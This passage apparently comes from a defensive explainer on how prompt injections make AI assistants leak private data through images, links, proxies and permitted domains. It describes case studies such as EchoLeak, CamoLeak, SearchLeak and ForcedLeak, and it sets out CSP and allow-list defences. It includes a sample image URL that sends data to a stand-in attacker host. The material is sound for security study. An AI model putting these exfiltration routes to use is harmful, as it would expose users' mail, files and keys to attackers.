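*Hidden-in-Plain-Text* (Guo and Wei, January 2026) is a benchmark that measures the effect of cleaning in a system that looks up web pages and gives relevant passages to a model. It contains 6,200 pages built in the style of social media, with instructions in hidden elements, off-screen text, image descriptions, labels for screen readers, and zero-width characters. About half the pages used visible variants. The models tested were open models from the Llama, Mistral and Qwen families, with 7 to 70 billion parameters, and all are now old. In every setting, the prompt included an instruction not to follow instructions in the retrieved text.

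Guo and Wei tested one cleaner for page markup and another for characters. The "all defenses" setting combined both with a rule that every sentence of the answer must cite a retrieved passage. The attack success rate, which is the share of attempts in which the model followed the planted instruction, changed as follows:

| Place of the instruction | No cleaning | Markup cleaner | Character cleaner | All defenses |
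|---|---|---|---|---|
| Hidden elements | 34.0% | 12.3% | 33.1% | 5.0% |
| Off-screen text | 30.1% | 9.8% | 29.3% | 4.6% |
| Image descriptions | 27.8% | 11.1% | 27.0% | 4.8% |
| Screen-reader labels | 9.6% | 9.3% | 9.4% | 5.1% |
| Zero-width characters | 23.2% | 23.0% | 7.8% | 4.2% |
| Average | 24.9% | 13.1% | 21.3% | 4.7% |

Each cleaner helped only against the kind of hiding it targeted, and neither did much about screen-reader labels. Guo and Wei don't report an attack rate for the two cleaners together without the citation rule. Averaging the better cleaner's result in each row gives about 10 percent, so much of the further drop to 4.7 percent probably comes from the citation rule, which depends on the model's behavior.

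The markup cleaner added only 3.1 percent to the response time, and the character cleaner added less than 0.5 percent. With both in place, the share of questions the system could answer fell by only about two percentage points. In tests on 2,350 real web pages with all the defenses in place, attacks rewritten to get around them succeeded 5.4 percent of the time, compared with 4.3 percent for the original attacks. Of the attacks that still succeeded despite the defenses, 49 percent were commands in the visible text of the page.

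### Visible and encrypted instructions

Cleaning cannot remove a visible command without also removing text the user wants. In Barach's tests, every injection that escaped detection was visible. Barach sees this as a dilemma for the attacker, since a recruiter might open the résumé and read the injection. That risk deters attackers less when people use the assistant to avoid reading, as Maria does with her morning mail.

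The full set of filters still let 16.7 percent of Barach's attacks succeed. Putting the résumé between delimiters that marked it as data reduced that to zero, but the tests used a simulated screener designed to ignore any instructions between the delimiters, whereas a real model might follow them.

An attacker can also send text that is visible but unreadable. In *Zero-click Grok data theft* (August 2026), the security company Adversa AI described such an attack on Grok. A web page contained an encrypted message and what Grok needed to decrypt it. When a user asked for a summary of the page, Grok decrypted the message with its code tool and followed the instructions inside. It then sent the attacker the user's name, approximate location and prompts from the conversation by opening a web address that contained them.

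Everything on that page was visible, so a cleaner had nothing to strip, and a filter that scans for suspicious phrases would have found only scrambled characters. The page also included the instructions for decoding them. *Reverse CAPTCHA* assumes that an attacker who controls only a document cannot give the model such hints, and the Grok case suggests that this assumption is too optimistic for models that can run code.

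Adversa AI reported the problem to xAI on June 3 and could still reproduce it on August 19. Ars Technica's *Grok exfiltrates user data when malicious instructions are encrypted* (2026) reported that Grok was still leaking data when the article appeared the next day. A filter that checked the code tool's output before the model read it, as Schwarz's rule would require, might have caught the decrypted instructions, but only if it recognized them as instructions. Adversa AI, which sells protection for AI agents, recommends asking the user before an agent contacts a new destination. This check works even if nobody has detected the injection.

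## Limiting the images and links a chat window displays

A chat window can also stop a theft without detecting the injection behind it, as Maria's could have done by leaving out the image.

### From Markdown to a network request

A chat program converts the model's Markdown into HTML, the language of web pages. In Markdown, square brackets followed by an address in parentheses make a link. An exclamation mark in front of the brackets makes an image instead:

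- Link: `[Sales chart](https://example.com/chart.png)`
- Image: `![Sales chart](https://example.com/chart.png)`

Only one character differs, but the image loads without a click. The conversion usually happens while the model is still writing:

1. The server sends the answer to the browser in small pieces.
2. After each piece, a script on the page converts the text received so far into page elements.
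3. Once the image's address is complete, the script creates an image element.
4. The browser requests the address, often before the rest of the answer has arrived.

Checkmarx's *Exploiting Markdown Injection in AI agents* describes a demonstration in which Microsoft's Copilot Chat leaked a secret key from a programmer's files. No image appeared in the chat, but the request for it still reached the researchers' server. The trick is almost as old as ChatGPT. Willison (2023), in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, credits Roman Samoilenko with a version that used a single-pixel image.

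Browsers request an image as soon as a script creates an image element and gives it an address, even if the script hasn't yet added the element to the page. Before creating the element, a chat program therefore has to decide whether to allow the image.

### Five restrictions compared

Chat programs can restrict images and links in several ways:

| Restriction | What it prevents | What can still leak data | Cost to the user |
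|---|---|---|---|
| No images | All leaks through images that load by themselves | Links the user clicks | No charts, screenshots or photographs |
| Images from listed sites only | Requests for images on the attacker's own server | Listed sites that store or forward what they receive, and links | Most pictures from the wider web |
| Links as plain text with the full address | Links whose wording hides their destination | Addresses the user opens without reading them closely | Long addresses in the answer, and extra copying |
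| A click before loading | Requests the user didn't ask for | Anything the user approves without checking | Frequent interruptions |
| Fetching through a proxy | The site learning the user's network address | Data in the image's address, unless the proxy refuses to pass it on | Slower loading |

The first two are deterministic rules that work without any action from the user. Showing full addresses and asking for a click both depend on the user's judgment. If the assistant gave Maria a link labeled "delivery schedule", she would have no reason to suspect that its address contained the title of a confidential plan. The full address might alert her, but an attacker can have the model encode the title as a string of letters and digits, and many harmless links contain such strings.

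A proxy, which is a server that fetches content for a user or page, is the weakest of the five against exfiltration. Websites use image proxies mainly for privacy, because the outside server then receives the proxy's network address instead of the visitor's. But the proxy still has to request the image's URL, which contains the stolen data. Nudge Security's *CamoLeak* (2025) describes a 2025 flaw in which GitHub's own image proxy carried private code out. A proxy stops this kind of theft only if it also refuses suspicious URLs.

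Few products restrict links as strictly as images. Google's Gemini doesn't display images from outside addresses, but it does display clickable links. When Checkmarx reported in October 2025 that an injection could put private data into such a link, Google closed the report as "Won't Fix (Infeasible)". Gemini removes links that Google knows to be malicious, but an attacker can get around this by registering a new domain. Salesforce went further that year after a leak from its own AI agent. According to Willison, it introduced a list of trusted addresses and stopped the agent from producing links to any others. That is practical for a sales tool that mostly refers to a company's own records, but it would make a general assistant that people use to search the web much less useful.

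The first restriction suits an office assistant such as Maria's. If users need pictures, the program can still show those stored on the company's own server, as long as outsiders can't read that server's logs.

### GitHub Copilot Chat's list of trusted sites

GitHub Copilot Chat, an assistant that answers questions about code, had the flaw in early 2024. It could read both a programmer's private code and files from strangers, and it displayed Markdown images. Rehberger reported the problem on February 25. GitHub confirmed it on March 6 and said it was already tracking the bug internally. It confirmed a fix on June 12.

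GitHub's fix was an allow-list for images, which load by themselves. According to Willison's *GitHub Copilot Chat*, the program stopped displaying images from untrusted domains. The summary in Vulners' *GitHub*, an entry in a database of software flaws, also mentions a window that informs users about a link before they click it.

Rehberger had the impression that Copilot Chat no longer displayed images at all, according to Embrace The Red's *GitHub Copilot Chat*. This was an easy mistake, because an image on a tester's own server fails to load whether the chat blocks all images or only those from sites that aren't permitted. Under the second rule, an attacker can still look for a permitted site that passes data on, and CamoLeak used such a route. On August 14, 2025, fourteen months after the first fix, GitHub turned off images in Copilot Chat entirely. MintMCP calls this blunt, since it removed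 a useful feature, but agrees that it closed the route CamoLeak had used.

### Why filters miss links

A program might instead search the model's answer for dangerous links and delete them before converting it. This is harder than it sounds because Markdown has several ways to write the same link:

| Form | Example |
|---|---|
| Inline | `[report](https://example.com/report)` |
| Reference | `[report][1]`, with `[1]: https://example.com/report` on another line |
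| Bare address | `<https://example.com/report>` |
| HTML, which many Markdown programs also accept | `<a href="https://example.com/report">report</a>` |

A filter written for the inline form misses the second row, where the address is on a separate line. Images also have inline, reference and HTML forms. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* reports that the EchoLeak researchers used the reference form first for a link and then for an image that loaded without a click.

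A developer could add a pattern for each form, but Markdown programs differ in what they accept, and the filter has to match the one that renders the page. It is safer to let that program convert the text first and then check the resulting HTML. All four links in the table produce the same element with the same address, so one rule covers them. The rule should allow only listed elements and addresses, because HTML has other elements that load outside content, including video, embedded pages and style sheets.

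Displaying the answer piece by piece also makes filtering harder. A filter that examines each piece separately can miss an address split between two of them. With the reference form, the line containing the address may arrive at the end and turn an earlier pair of brackets into a working link or image after the filter has passed it. The filter can avoid both problems by rechecking the whole answer so far after each piece. Checking once, when the answer is complete, works only if the browser displays nothing before the check.

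### SearchLeak

*SearchLeak*, published by the data security company Varonis on June 15, 2026, explains how three weaknesses in Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search together let an attacker steal information from an employee who clicked one link.

The link led to Microsoft's website, so tools that screen for fraudulent links let it through. Its address contained a query that Copilot ran as soon as the page opened. The query was meant for search terms, but Copilot also followed instructions in it. An attacker could have Copilot search the employee's email, take the subject line of a message and put it into the address of an image in the answer. Subject lines are worth stealing because many services send login codes in them. Copilot searched with the employee's access rights, so an attacker could also get at meeting notes, salary data and other company files.

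Microsoft had anticipated dangerous HTML in Copilot's answers, so its program wrapped the answer in a code block, which makes the browser show HTML as text instead of acting on it. But the program added the code block only after Copilot had finished. While the answer was still arriving, the browser acted on the HTML and requested the image. By the time the employee saw a harmless line of code, the browser had already sent the request. Programmers call this a race condition, because the outcome depends on which of two events happens first.

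The second obstacle was Microsoft's content security policy (CSP), a rule that a website sends to the browser to limit the addresses from which a page may load images, scripts and other content. The policy blocked images from the attacker's server but allowed them from Bing, Microsoft's search engine. Bing can search for pictures similar to one whose address the user supplies, and its server has to fetch that picture to analyze it. The image in Copilot's answer therefore pointed to Bing, and the request included the attacker's address, which contained the stolen title. The browser contacted Bing, as the policy allowed. Bing then contacted the attacker's server, and the policy could not block that request because it applied only to the browser.

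Fixing any one of these weaknesses would have stopped the attack. If the program had cleaned the answer before displaying it, the browser would never have requested the image. If the policy had left out Bing, or if Bing had refused to fetch the address, the request would not have reached the attacker. Varonis recommends cleaning answers at the moment of display and reviewing every permitted domain for services that fetch addresses supplied by users. A program can follow the first recommendation and still display answers gradually, by showing words as they arrive and holding back only the images until it has checked them. Most readers would hardly notice the delay.

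Microsoft patched the flaw and rated it critical. The Next Web reports a severity score of 6.5 out of 10, which would have been higher if the attack didn't require a click. The Hacker News (2026) points out that Microsoft runs the service, so a company's administrators cannot change the parts that failed. They can watch for search links that contain HTML and for unusual requests to Bing's image service, and they can limit how many files Copilot may search.

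### When someone else's program displays the answer

Many people talk to AI agents through messaging apps such as Slack or Telegram, where the agent's developer doesn't control the window that shows the answer. These apps may also fetch addresses for reasons unrelated to AI. For example, when a message contains a link, they often request the address so they can show a preview with the page's title and a small picture.

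An ordinary link can leak data without a click if the messaging app previews it. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* notes that the preview makes the same type of request as a click would. The attacker only has to get the agent to write a link with private data in its address. Removing every image from the agent's answers doesn't prevent this, because the attack doesn't use one.

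OpenClaw, a widely used personal AI agent, was vulnerable with its default Telegram settings. PromptArmor found that turning off link previews in OpenClaw's configuration stopped the data from reaching its test site. Users lose only the preview and can still open the link. PromptArmor would like messaging apps to offer this setting for individual chats, so that people could keep previews in conversations with colleagues. It also runs a public test site where users can check their own combination of agent and app.

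Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft agent that carries out longer office tasks, had a similar problem even though Microsoft makes both the agent and the programs that display its messages. According to Microsoft's documentation, Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or posts a message in the chat program Teams. PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, which Willison discussed in May 2026, found that Cowork sent messages without asking when the recipient was the user, and that users had no setting to change this.

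Messages to oneself could expose data to others, even though the exception for them seems reasonable. Outlook and Teams loaded outside images in these messages, so opening one could send a request to a stranger's server. PromptArmor tested this with a skill, a file of instructions that teaches the agent a recurring task. People often download skills that others have shared online. Five of the file's 81 lines contained the injection. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, Cowork collected download links for recent documents and sent the user a Teams message with images whose addresses contained those links. The links worked without a login, so once the user opened the message, the attacker could download the files themselves.

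The attack succeeded in all five trials, in which Cowork chose automatically between two Claude models, Opus 4.7 and Sonnet 4.6. When PromptArmor selected Opus 4.7, the more advanced of the two, the same injection worked and the agent leaked more documents because it searched for recent files more thoroughly. Five trials are too few for a precise success rate, but using a strong model did not make up for the weakness in the display.

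Asking for approval would have helped only if the user could see what the message contained. Cowork's action log listed the Teams message it had sent but didn't show the images inside. Cowork can also run tasks on a schedule, when nobody is there to approve them. A fixed rule would be more reliable. Outlook and Teams could leave external images out of any message an agent has written, or Cowork could remove them before sending.

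PromptArmor treats the problem as a risk of the product's design instead of a single bug, and does not report a fix. It suggests that administrators block file downloads from sensitive sites, which makes the stolen links useless. This has a major drawback: employees can then view those files only in a browser and can't open them in Word or Excel.

### ReLeak

On December 3, 2026, *ReLeak* (Simonovich, 2026) disclosed three more ways to get data out of Microsoft 365 Copilot. Simonovich works at Cato AI Labs, the research team that found EchoLeak a year earlier, when the team had a different name. Like Maria's supplier, the attacker first sends an email with hidden instructions. The employee doesn't have to open it, because Copilot reads it while looking for material to answer an ordinary question and then follows the instructions.

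The three attacks differ in how the data leaves. The table draws on Faisal (2026), in *An Unread Email Could Turn Microsoft 365 Copilot Into a Data Thief*, and Antipov (2026), in *Письмо даже не нужно открывать*:

| What carried the data | Step that failed | Fixed in 2026 |
|---|---|---|
| An image in Copilot's answer | The browser loaded the image from Bing, which contacted the attacker's server | November 15 |
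| A link in a document that Copilot created | Microsoft's servers requested the link while processing the stored file | November 11 |
| A program that Copilot wrote and ran | The sandbox, a closed environment for running code, let traffic out | September 17 |

Microsoft made all three fixes on its own servers, so customers have nothing to install. Cato knows of no attacks on real customers.

The first attack repeats the final step of SearchLeak but doesn't require a click. Microsoft had patched SearchLeak by mid-June, before Cato sent its reports between July 29 and August 20. That patch evidently left open at least one route through Bing, which Microsoft didn't close until November. Blocking every outside image in Copilot's answers, including those from Bing, would have stopped both attacks at the display stage.

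No restriction on the chat window would have stopped the second attack. Copilot put the data into a link in a Word, Excel, PowerPoint or PDF file and saved the file to the company's storage. Antipov writes that in Cato's tests, Microsoft's servers requested the link one to eight minutes after the conversation ended, even if the employee never opened the document. Neither the chat window nor the browser made the request. To prevent this, Microsoft would have to apply the same rules about addresses to every service that handles what Copilot writes, including services built long before Copilot.

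The third attack sent data straight from the sandbox to an outside server, without displaying anything. According to Microsoft's documentation, the sandbox allows no network traffic in either direction, but the researchers got around this restriction. Microsoft fixed this flaw first. Its severity score was raised from 7.4 to 8.6 out of 10. Agents that customers build with two other Microsoft tools also use a code interpreter, though nobody has confirmed that the flaw affected those agents.

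Cato's researchers used AI agents to find these weaknesses. Under human direction, the agents wrote test cases, analyzed Copilot's refusals and adjusted the next attempt. Attackers can automate the search in the same way, so a forgotten service on a list of permitted sites is less likely to stay unnoticed.

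## Content security policies

Microsoft's content security policy included the list of approved sites that let SearchLeak's requests through to Bing. Google, GitHub, Salesforce and the email company Superhuman have also relied on such policies to stop their assistants' answers from loading images from unapproved servers. In each case, researchers got data out through an approved site.

### Who writes the policy and who enforces it

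A website's operator writes the policy, the site's server sends it with the page, and the visitor's browser enforces it. The policy normally arrives in a header, a line of information sent before the page. The operator can also write it into the page's HTML, but then the browser doesn't apply it to anything earlier in the page.

The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) publishes the standard for these policies. The current draft, *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2026), presents CSP mainly as protection against cross-site scripting, in which an attacker gets a website to run the attacker's own script. The draft describes CSP as a way to limit the damage after a site's other checks have failed, not as a replacement for them. A chat product uses CSP in much the same way. After the model has followed a planted instruction, the browser blocks the last step of the attack.

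A policy for a chat page at `https://chat.example.com` might look like this:

```
Content-Security-Policy:
  default-src 'none';
  script-src 'self';
  style-src 'self';
  img-src 'self' https://images.example.com;
  connect-src 'self';
  frame-src 'none';
  form-action 'self'
```

A real header would normally be written on one line. Each part between semicolons is a directive, which names a type of request and the places it may go. The keyword `'none'` permits nothing, and `'self'` stands for the page's own origin. An origin is the scheme (such as https), host and port that browsers use together to tell one website from another.

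| Directive | What it limits | What this policy permits |
|---|---|---|
| default-src | Types of content without a directive of their own here, such as fonts and video | Nothing |
| img-src | Images | The chat site and one image server |
| connect-src | Requests by the page's scripts, including those that send Maria's question and fetch the answer | The chat site |
| frame-src | Other web pages displayed inside this one | Nothing |
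| form-action | Addresses to which a form on the page may send its contents | The chat site |

The other two directives allow the page to use its own scripts and style sheets.

The default applies only where the policy lacks a more specific directive. If an operator wrote `default-src 'none'; img-src *`, the asterisk would permit images from anywhere despite the strict default. W3C warns that a policy protects against exfiltration only as well as its least restrictive directive. Leaving out the default is also risky, because some requests have no directive of their own, such as prefetching, where the browser loads something in advance in case the user needs it. The default doesn't cover forms, so an operator who omits `form-action` lets forms send their contents anywhere.

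Operators can test a policy in report-only mode, in which the browser reports violations but blocks nothing. They can also collect reports once the policy is in force, and a sudden run of blocked images would be good evidence that someone is trying an injection. The reports need careful handling because each contains the blocked address, including its parameters. A report about Maria's image would therefore copy the title of the Leeds plan into the operator's logs.

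### A permitted image and a forbidden one

Suppose Maria's chat page has this policy and the assistant's answer contains two images:

- `https://images.example.com/sales.png`
- `https://stranger.example/pixel.png?title=Leeds`

The browser handles them as follows:

1. The chat program creates an image element for each address.
2. Before contacting either server, the browser looks up the directive for images, `img-src`.
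3. It compares each address with the entries there. The first matches `https://images.example.com`, and the second matches nothing.
4. It requests the first image and displays it. It sends no request for the second, so Maria sees at most an empty square and the stranger's server receives nothing.
5. If the permitted server redirects the browser to a different address, the browser checks the new address before continuing.

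An entry can also name a folder or file on a server, but the browser ignores that part after a redirect so that a malicious website can't use its own policy to discover where another site redirected the visitor. An entry for one folder therefore permits everything on the server whenever another permitted site redirects to that server.

### Why the policy survives a fooled model

The policy is a deterministic rule, so the wording of the supplier's email can't change the browser's decision. It also arrived with the page, before the assistant wrote its answer. Even if the answer contained HTML with a second, looser policy, the browser would enforce both, so the second policy couldn't allow a request that the first one blocks.

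However, the browser checks where a request is going, not what data it contains. An entry can specify a host and a path, but not the parameters after a question mark. If the assistant put the title of the Leeds plan into an address on `images.example.com`, the browser would send the request just as it would send one for the sales chart. The policy therefore protects Maria only if no attacker can learn what reaches the permitted servers. That condition failed in four ways in 2025 and early 2026.

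### EchoLeak: a permitted service that fetched other addresses

EchoLeak, the 2025 flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, began with an email much like the one Maria received. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reconstructs from public accounts how the attack got past one defense after another. Microsoft's injection classifier missed the email because it read like a request to its human recipient. A filter that removed outside links from Copilot's answers missed links in the reference form. The CSP then blocked the browser from loading an image from the attacker's server.

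The researchers, from a team then called Aim Labs, got around the policy using a Microsoft Teams preview service. The policy allowed requests to the service, which would fetch any address passed to it as a parameter. The browser sent the stolen data to Teams, which forwarded it to the attacker's server. Microsoft's policy did not account for a Microsoft server forwarding requests elsewhere.

Microsoft deployed a fix on its own servers in May 2025, before the public disclosure on June 11, so customers had nothing to install. Reddy and Gujral report that Microsoft has also begun removing reference-style links and embedded images from outside content before Copilot reads it. But the underlying problem returned a year later, when SearchLeak used Bing in the same way.

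### CamoLeak: a message in the order of requests

GitHub had a stronger defense against such forwarding. Its policy permitted images only from domains that GitHub owned, but many software projects include pictures from elsewhere in their documentation, so GitHub fetches those through its own proxy, Camo. When processing a file, GitHub replaces each outside image address with a Camo address that includes a signature, a code that only GitHub can compute. Camo refuses any request without a valid signature. A model can write a new address containing stolen text but cannot sign it, so the method used in EchoLeak would have failed here.

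A Legit Security researcher, who found the flaw in June 2025, got around the signatures by having GitHub sign a set of image addresses in advance, one for each letter and symbol. A hidden comment then led Copilot Chat to display these images in an order that spelled out private text. Camo fetched each image from the researcher's server, so the researcher could read the text from the order of the requests. The images were single transparent pixels, so the user saw nothing unusual.

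The signatures prevented attackers from putting new data into an address. GitHub had assumed that this would keep data from getting out, but choosing among fixed addresses also conveys information. One choice among $n$ equally likely addresses carries

$$\log_2 n \text{ bits}$$

With 64 addresses, each image carries 6 bits, enough to identify one of 64 characters, so a secret key of 40 such characters would take 40 images. In the demonstrations, the researcher extracted a password-like key for a cloud service and the description of an unpublished security flaw.

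GitHub responded by turning off images in Copilot Chat, but it could have tried to improve its signatures instead. Reddy and Gujral recommend a proxy whose signatures expire, which they say stops automatic leaks, based on a theoretical comparison of defenses. An attacker's prepared addresses would eventually stop working, but the attacker could obtain new ones and write a new injection. Signatures valid only within one user's conversation would be harder to prepare in advance. Even then, GitHub would have to avoid signing addresses just because the model had written them, since Camo would then fetch any address the attacker wanted.

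### ForcedLeak: a permitted domain with a new owner

Salesforce's Agentforce product lets businesses build AI agents that work with their customer records. In 2025, the security company Noma Security showed that an attacker could place an injection in a web form for prospective customers. When an employee later asked the agent about the contact created from that form, the agent also followed the planted instructions. It collected other contacts' email addresses and put them into an image's URL.

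Salesforce's policy blocked images from unknown sites but permitted every subdomain of `my-salesforce-cms.com`, which Salesforce had once had good reason to trust. The domain's registration had expired, so Noma's researchers registered it and received the data. Browsers enforce the policy by comparing domain names, so they can't detect a change of owner. Encryption doesn't help, because the new owner can obtain a valid certificate.

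The flaw received a severity score of 9.4 out of 10, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Critical Vulnerability in Salesforce AgentForce Exposed*. Salesforce regained control of the domain and, as Willison describes, audited and corrected its policy. It also introduced a separate list of trusted addresses for its agents' output, as The Hacker News reported in *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak* (2025). That list would have the same weakness if it contained an abandoned domain.

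### Superhuman: a permitted site that stored what it received

Superhuman's email program has an AI assistant. The program's content security policy allowed images from `docs.google.com`, which also hosts Google Forms, a survey tool. A Google Forms link can contain answers and submit them when opened. PromptArmor's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails* (January 2026) describes an injection that made the assistant put the user's emails in such a link and use it as the address of an image. When the browser tried to load the image, it submitted the emails to the researchers' form.

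Google Forms worked as Google had designed it, so the attack involved no expired domain or forwarding service. Superhuman's policy failed because it treated image requests as only retrieving data. Browsers request images with a method called GET, which by convention doesn't change anything on the server, but a server can still store what it receives. In PromptArmor's tests, the user only had to ask for a summary of recent mail. One answer leaked the full contents of several emails, and another leaked parts of more than 40.

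PromptArmor reported the flaw on the evening of Friday, December 5, 2025. Superhuman disabled the vulnerable features on Monday and deployed a first patch on Tuesday. It patched other parts of its products on December 18 and released another round of patches for further findings on January 11. PromptArmor praises the response but doesn't explain what the patches changed.

Google had made a similar mistake with its assistant Bard, whose policy allowed images from any subdomain of `google.com`. Willison's *Hacking Google Bard* describes a 2023 attack in which researchers collected the data through one of those subdomains, which lets anyone run a small program. The Google Forms route also worked against OpenAI's agent Codex in April 2026, according to PromptArmor's *Codex for Everything Exfiltrates Connected Data*. OpenAI has since fixed it. These cases suggest that developers tend to judge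 a host by the company that runs it, when they should also ask who can receive data there.

### What a policy leaves open

CSP has no directive that limits ordinary navigation. If the assistant gives Maria a link whose address contains the title of the Leeds plan, the browser will open the link when she clicks it. A script that manages to run on the page can also send the tab to a new address without a click. Browser developers once proposed a directive called `navigate-to` for such cases, but the current draft doesn't include it.

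The policy also has no effect on requests that a server makes. Superhuman's assistant could fetch web pages to answer questions about current events, and an injection could make it open an address containing data from the inbox. This request didn't pass through the user's browser, so Superhuman's policy couldn't block it, and PromptArmor could have sent the data to any host, not only to a Google host that the policy permitted.

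A content security policy also doesn't protect pages that come without one. PromptArmor found that Superhuman Go, another assistant from the same company, loaded an image directly from an attacker's domain. The assistant could read web pages and connected email accounts, so it often handled untrusted text and private data together.

W3C advises browsers not to let a page's content security policy interfere with extensions, because extensions act for the user, whose wishes take priority over the site's. An AI assistant that runs as an extension can therefore make requests that the page itself could not.

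Two less familiar routes matter mainly for products that run code written by the model. WebRTC, the technology behind video calls in browsers, can open connections that `default-src` doesn't control, and the W3C draft has a separate `webrtc` directive for blocking them. A page can also ask the browser to look up a server's numerical address in advance through the domain name system (DNS). The owner of a domain can see lookups of names under it, so data placed in a name can leak even if the browser never contacts the server.

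### One list for all of a page's connections

In *Connection Allowlists*, Google's Mike West, one of the editors of the CSP standard, proposes a simpler rule aimed at exfiltration. He argues that CSP divides requests into too many types for this purpose. A leak through a font is as bad as one through an image, so an operator who wants to stop leaks shouldn't have to decide about each type separately. He also objects that CSP misses some kinds of connection and that its way of describing permitted addresses makes policies long.

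The proposed header contains a single list:

```
Connection-Allowlist: (response-origin "https://images.example.com/*")
```

Here `response-origin` stands for the site that sent the page. Before the browser makes any connection for the page, it checks the destination against this list. Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial* (2026) says the mechanism covers navigation, redirects, WebRTC and early DNS lookups as well as ordinary requests. It gives AI-generated code as a main use. If a chat product runs a program the model wrote, the list can keep the program from sending data elsewhere.

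Google scheduled a trial on real websites for Chrome versions 148 to 151. Chrome for Developers' *FedCM* (2026), published in August, says Chrome 152 introduces the feature. It also warns that a strict list can break services that let people sign in with an account from another company, unless the operator adds those services to the list. The feature covers navigation, which could cause a similar problem for assistants that cite sources, because an operator can't list every website an answer might link to. A general assistant would therefore need to handle its links separately.

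Connection Allowlists are not yet a common web standard. West's draft is labeled an unofficial proposal outside the W3C standards track. In November 2025, West asked W3C's design reviewers to examine the idea and linked to requests seeking comment from Mozilla, which makes Firefox, and WebKit, Safari's engine (West, 2025). Operators whose users have different browsers therefore still need a CSP.

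Several details also remain unsettled. The draft blocks every redirected request, which West expects to be too strict for many real sites. It doesn't limit messages between windows or frames in the same browser. The list also applies to only one page, so an attacker who can run a script there might pass data to a less restricted page on the same site, which could then send it out. Sandboxing the page, which isolates it from the rest of the site, can prevent this.

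A complete list of connections would still have let through all four leaks described above if it had permitted the same addresses: Teams, Camo, a Salesforce domain and Google Docs. The proposal closes routes that CSP misses, but the operator must still decide whom to trust.

### Panels from other companies

Some chat products also display interactive panels from other companies, such as booking forms. The Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI assistants to outside tools, supports these panels through an extension called MCP Apps. The chat product displays each panel in a sandboxed iframe, a frame that the browser isolates from the surrounding page.

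The developer declares which servers the panel needs. One list covers requests made by scripts, and another covers the scripts themselves, style sheets, images and fonts, according to Model Context Protocol's *CSP & CORS*. Model Context Protocol's *Interface McpUiResourceCsp* describes further lists for embedded pages and the base address for relative links. The chat product builds the panel's CSP from these lists. Developers must list even the server that supplies the panel's own code, because the isolated frame has no website of its own to count as `'self'`.

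ChatGPT has a similar system. A reply in the forum thread *Trouble with CSP after publishing dev app* points out that OpenAI requires developers to declare these domains before they distribute an app widely, and that the sandbox blocks everything else. In *Verifying URLs used in apps*, a developer complains that ChatGPT warns users whenever they click a link from a panel to the developer's website. The reply points to an additional list of domains to which a panel may send users. This list covers clicks, which the panel's CSP would not restrict.

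The company that supplies a panel proposes the restrictions on it. This works well against an injection in an honest company's panel, since the planted text can't add the attacker's server to the list of declared domains, but it does little against a dishonest company, which can declare its own server and collect whatever the panel receives. The chat product's operator therefore has to review the declared domains and limit the data each panel gets. OpenAI's *Security &amp; Privacy* tells developers to request only the network permissions they need and to assume that injections will reach their servers.

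MCP Apps can impose a policy because the chat product loads the panel's HTML itself. When a frame comes directly from another company's server, that server normally sends the policy. Two proposals would give the surrounding page more control. The W3C's draft on embedded enforcement, *Content Security Policy* (2026), lets a page require a certain CSP from a frame it displays. Chrome's developers plan the same for the newer mechanism. *Intent to Prototype* describes an attribute that would let a page attach a connection list to a frame.

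### Rules for a sound allow-list

The failures above suggest five rules for pages that display a model's answers:

1. Permit a host only after checking every service on it, and leave it out if any of them fetches addresses supplied by others. EchoLeak needed just one such service. A host that only serves stored files is the safest choice. Limiting an entry to one folder is less reliable, because the browser ignores the folder after a redirect.
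2. Limit how many images an answer can load, even from permitted hosts. CamoLeak used one image per character, so a limit of three would have reduced the leak to three characters per answer. The chat program has to enforce this, since a CSP can't count requests.
3. Write out full host names instead of using wildcards, and check regularly that the company still controls each one. Salesforce's entry covered every subdomain of a domain it had lost. An automatic check of registration dates could have caught this before the researchers did.
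4. Exclude any host where a stranger can open an account and read what visitors send. This rules out the Google hosts used against Superhuman and Bard, and many other services for forms and shared files. If users need pictures from such a service, they can upload them to the chat product's own image server.
5. Send an equally strict policy with every page that displays a model's answers. Superhuman's email program blocked images from unknown domains, but Superhuman Go loaded them, so an attacker who targeted Superhuman Go didn't need a flaw in the list at all.

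## Checking the addresses an AI agent may fetch

Browsers enforce content security policies, but many of an agent's requests don't go through one. When Maria asks her assistant to look up a supplier, the program that opens the supplier's website usually runs on the AI company's servers. Radware's *ZombieAgent* describes a 2025 attack that got data out of ChatGPT through images in the user's browser and through OpenAI's servers. The researchers focused on the server method because the image method was less reliable and easier to block.

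A fetch on the provider's side has four steps:

1. The model writes a request to its fetching tool that includes an address.
2. A program on the provider's server reads the request.
3. The program contacts the website.
4. It adds the page's text to the conversation, and the model continues.

The model has no network connection of its own, so a check between the second and third steps covers every page the model opens with that tool, however persuasive the injection. Providers base this check on the site, a public record of the exact address, or where in the conversation the address came from.

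### Permitting listed domains

The simplest check uses an allow-list of domains:

1. Extract the host name from the address.
2. Look for it on the list, and refuse the request if it isn't there.
3. Fetch the page. If the server redirects to a different address, check that address too before following it.

Anthropic offers developers such a list for web_fetch, the tool its Claude models use to read web pages. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, an entry covers all subdomains, and a developer can narrow it to one part of a site. Anthropic recommends plain ASCII names, because a developer who pastes in a name with a Cyrillic "а" could permit a stranger's site whose address looks like Amazon's.

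OpenAI gives two reasons why such a list isn't enough. First, many reputable sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so a program that checks only the first address can end up at an attacker's server. Checking every redirect solves this. Second, people visit far more sites than any list contains, so they would see frequent warnings and learn to click through them without reading. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* reports that users of its coding agent, Claude Code, approved about 93 percent of permission requests, and that they paid less attention to each one as the number grew.

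A list of allowed sites also fails if an attacker can collect data through one of them, as happened with several content security policies. Willison's *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, a collection of his notes on such leaks, describes PromptArmor's November 2025 test of Antigravity, Google's code editor with a built-in agent. A web page posing as a technical guide contained instructions in text one pixel high. Google's Gemini model followed them, collected code and the keys to a cloud account, and used Antigravity's browser tool to open an address containing both.

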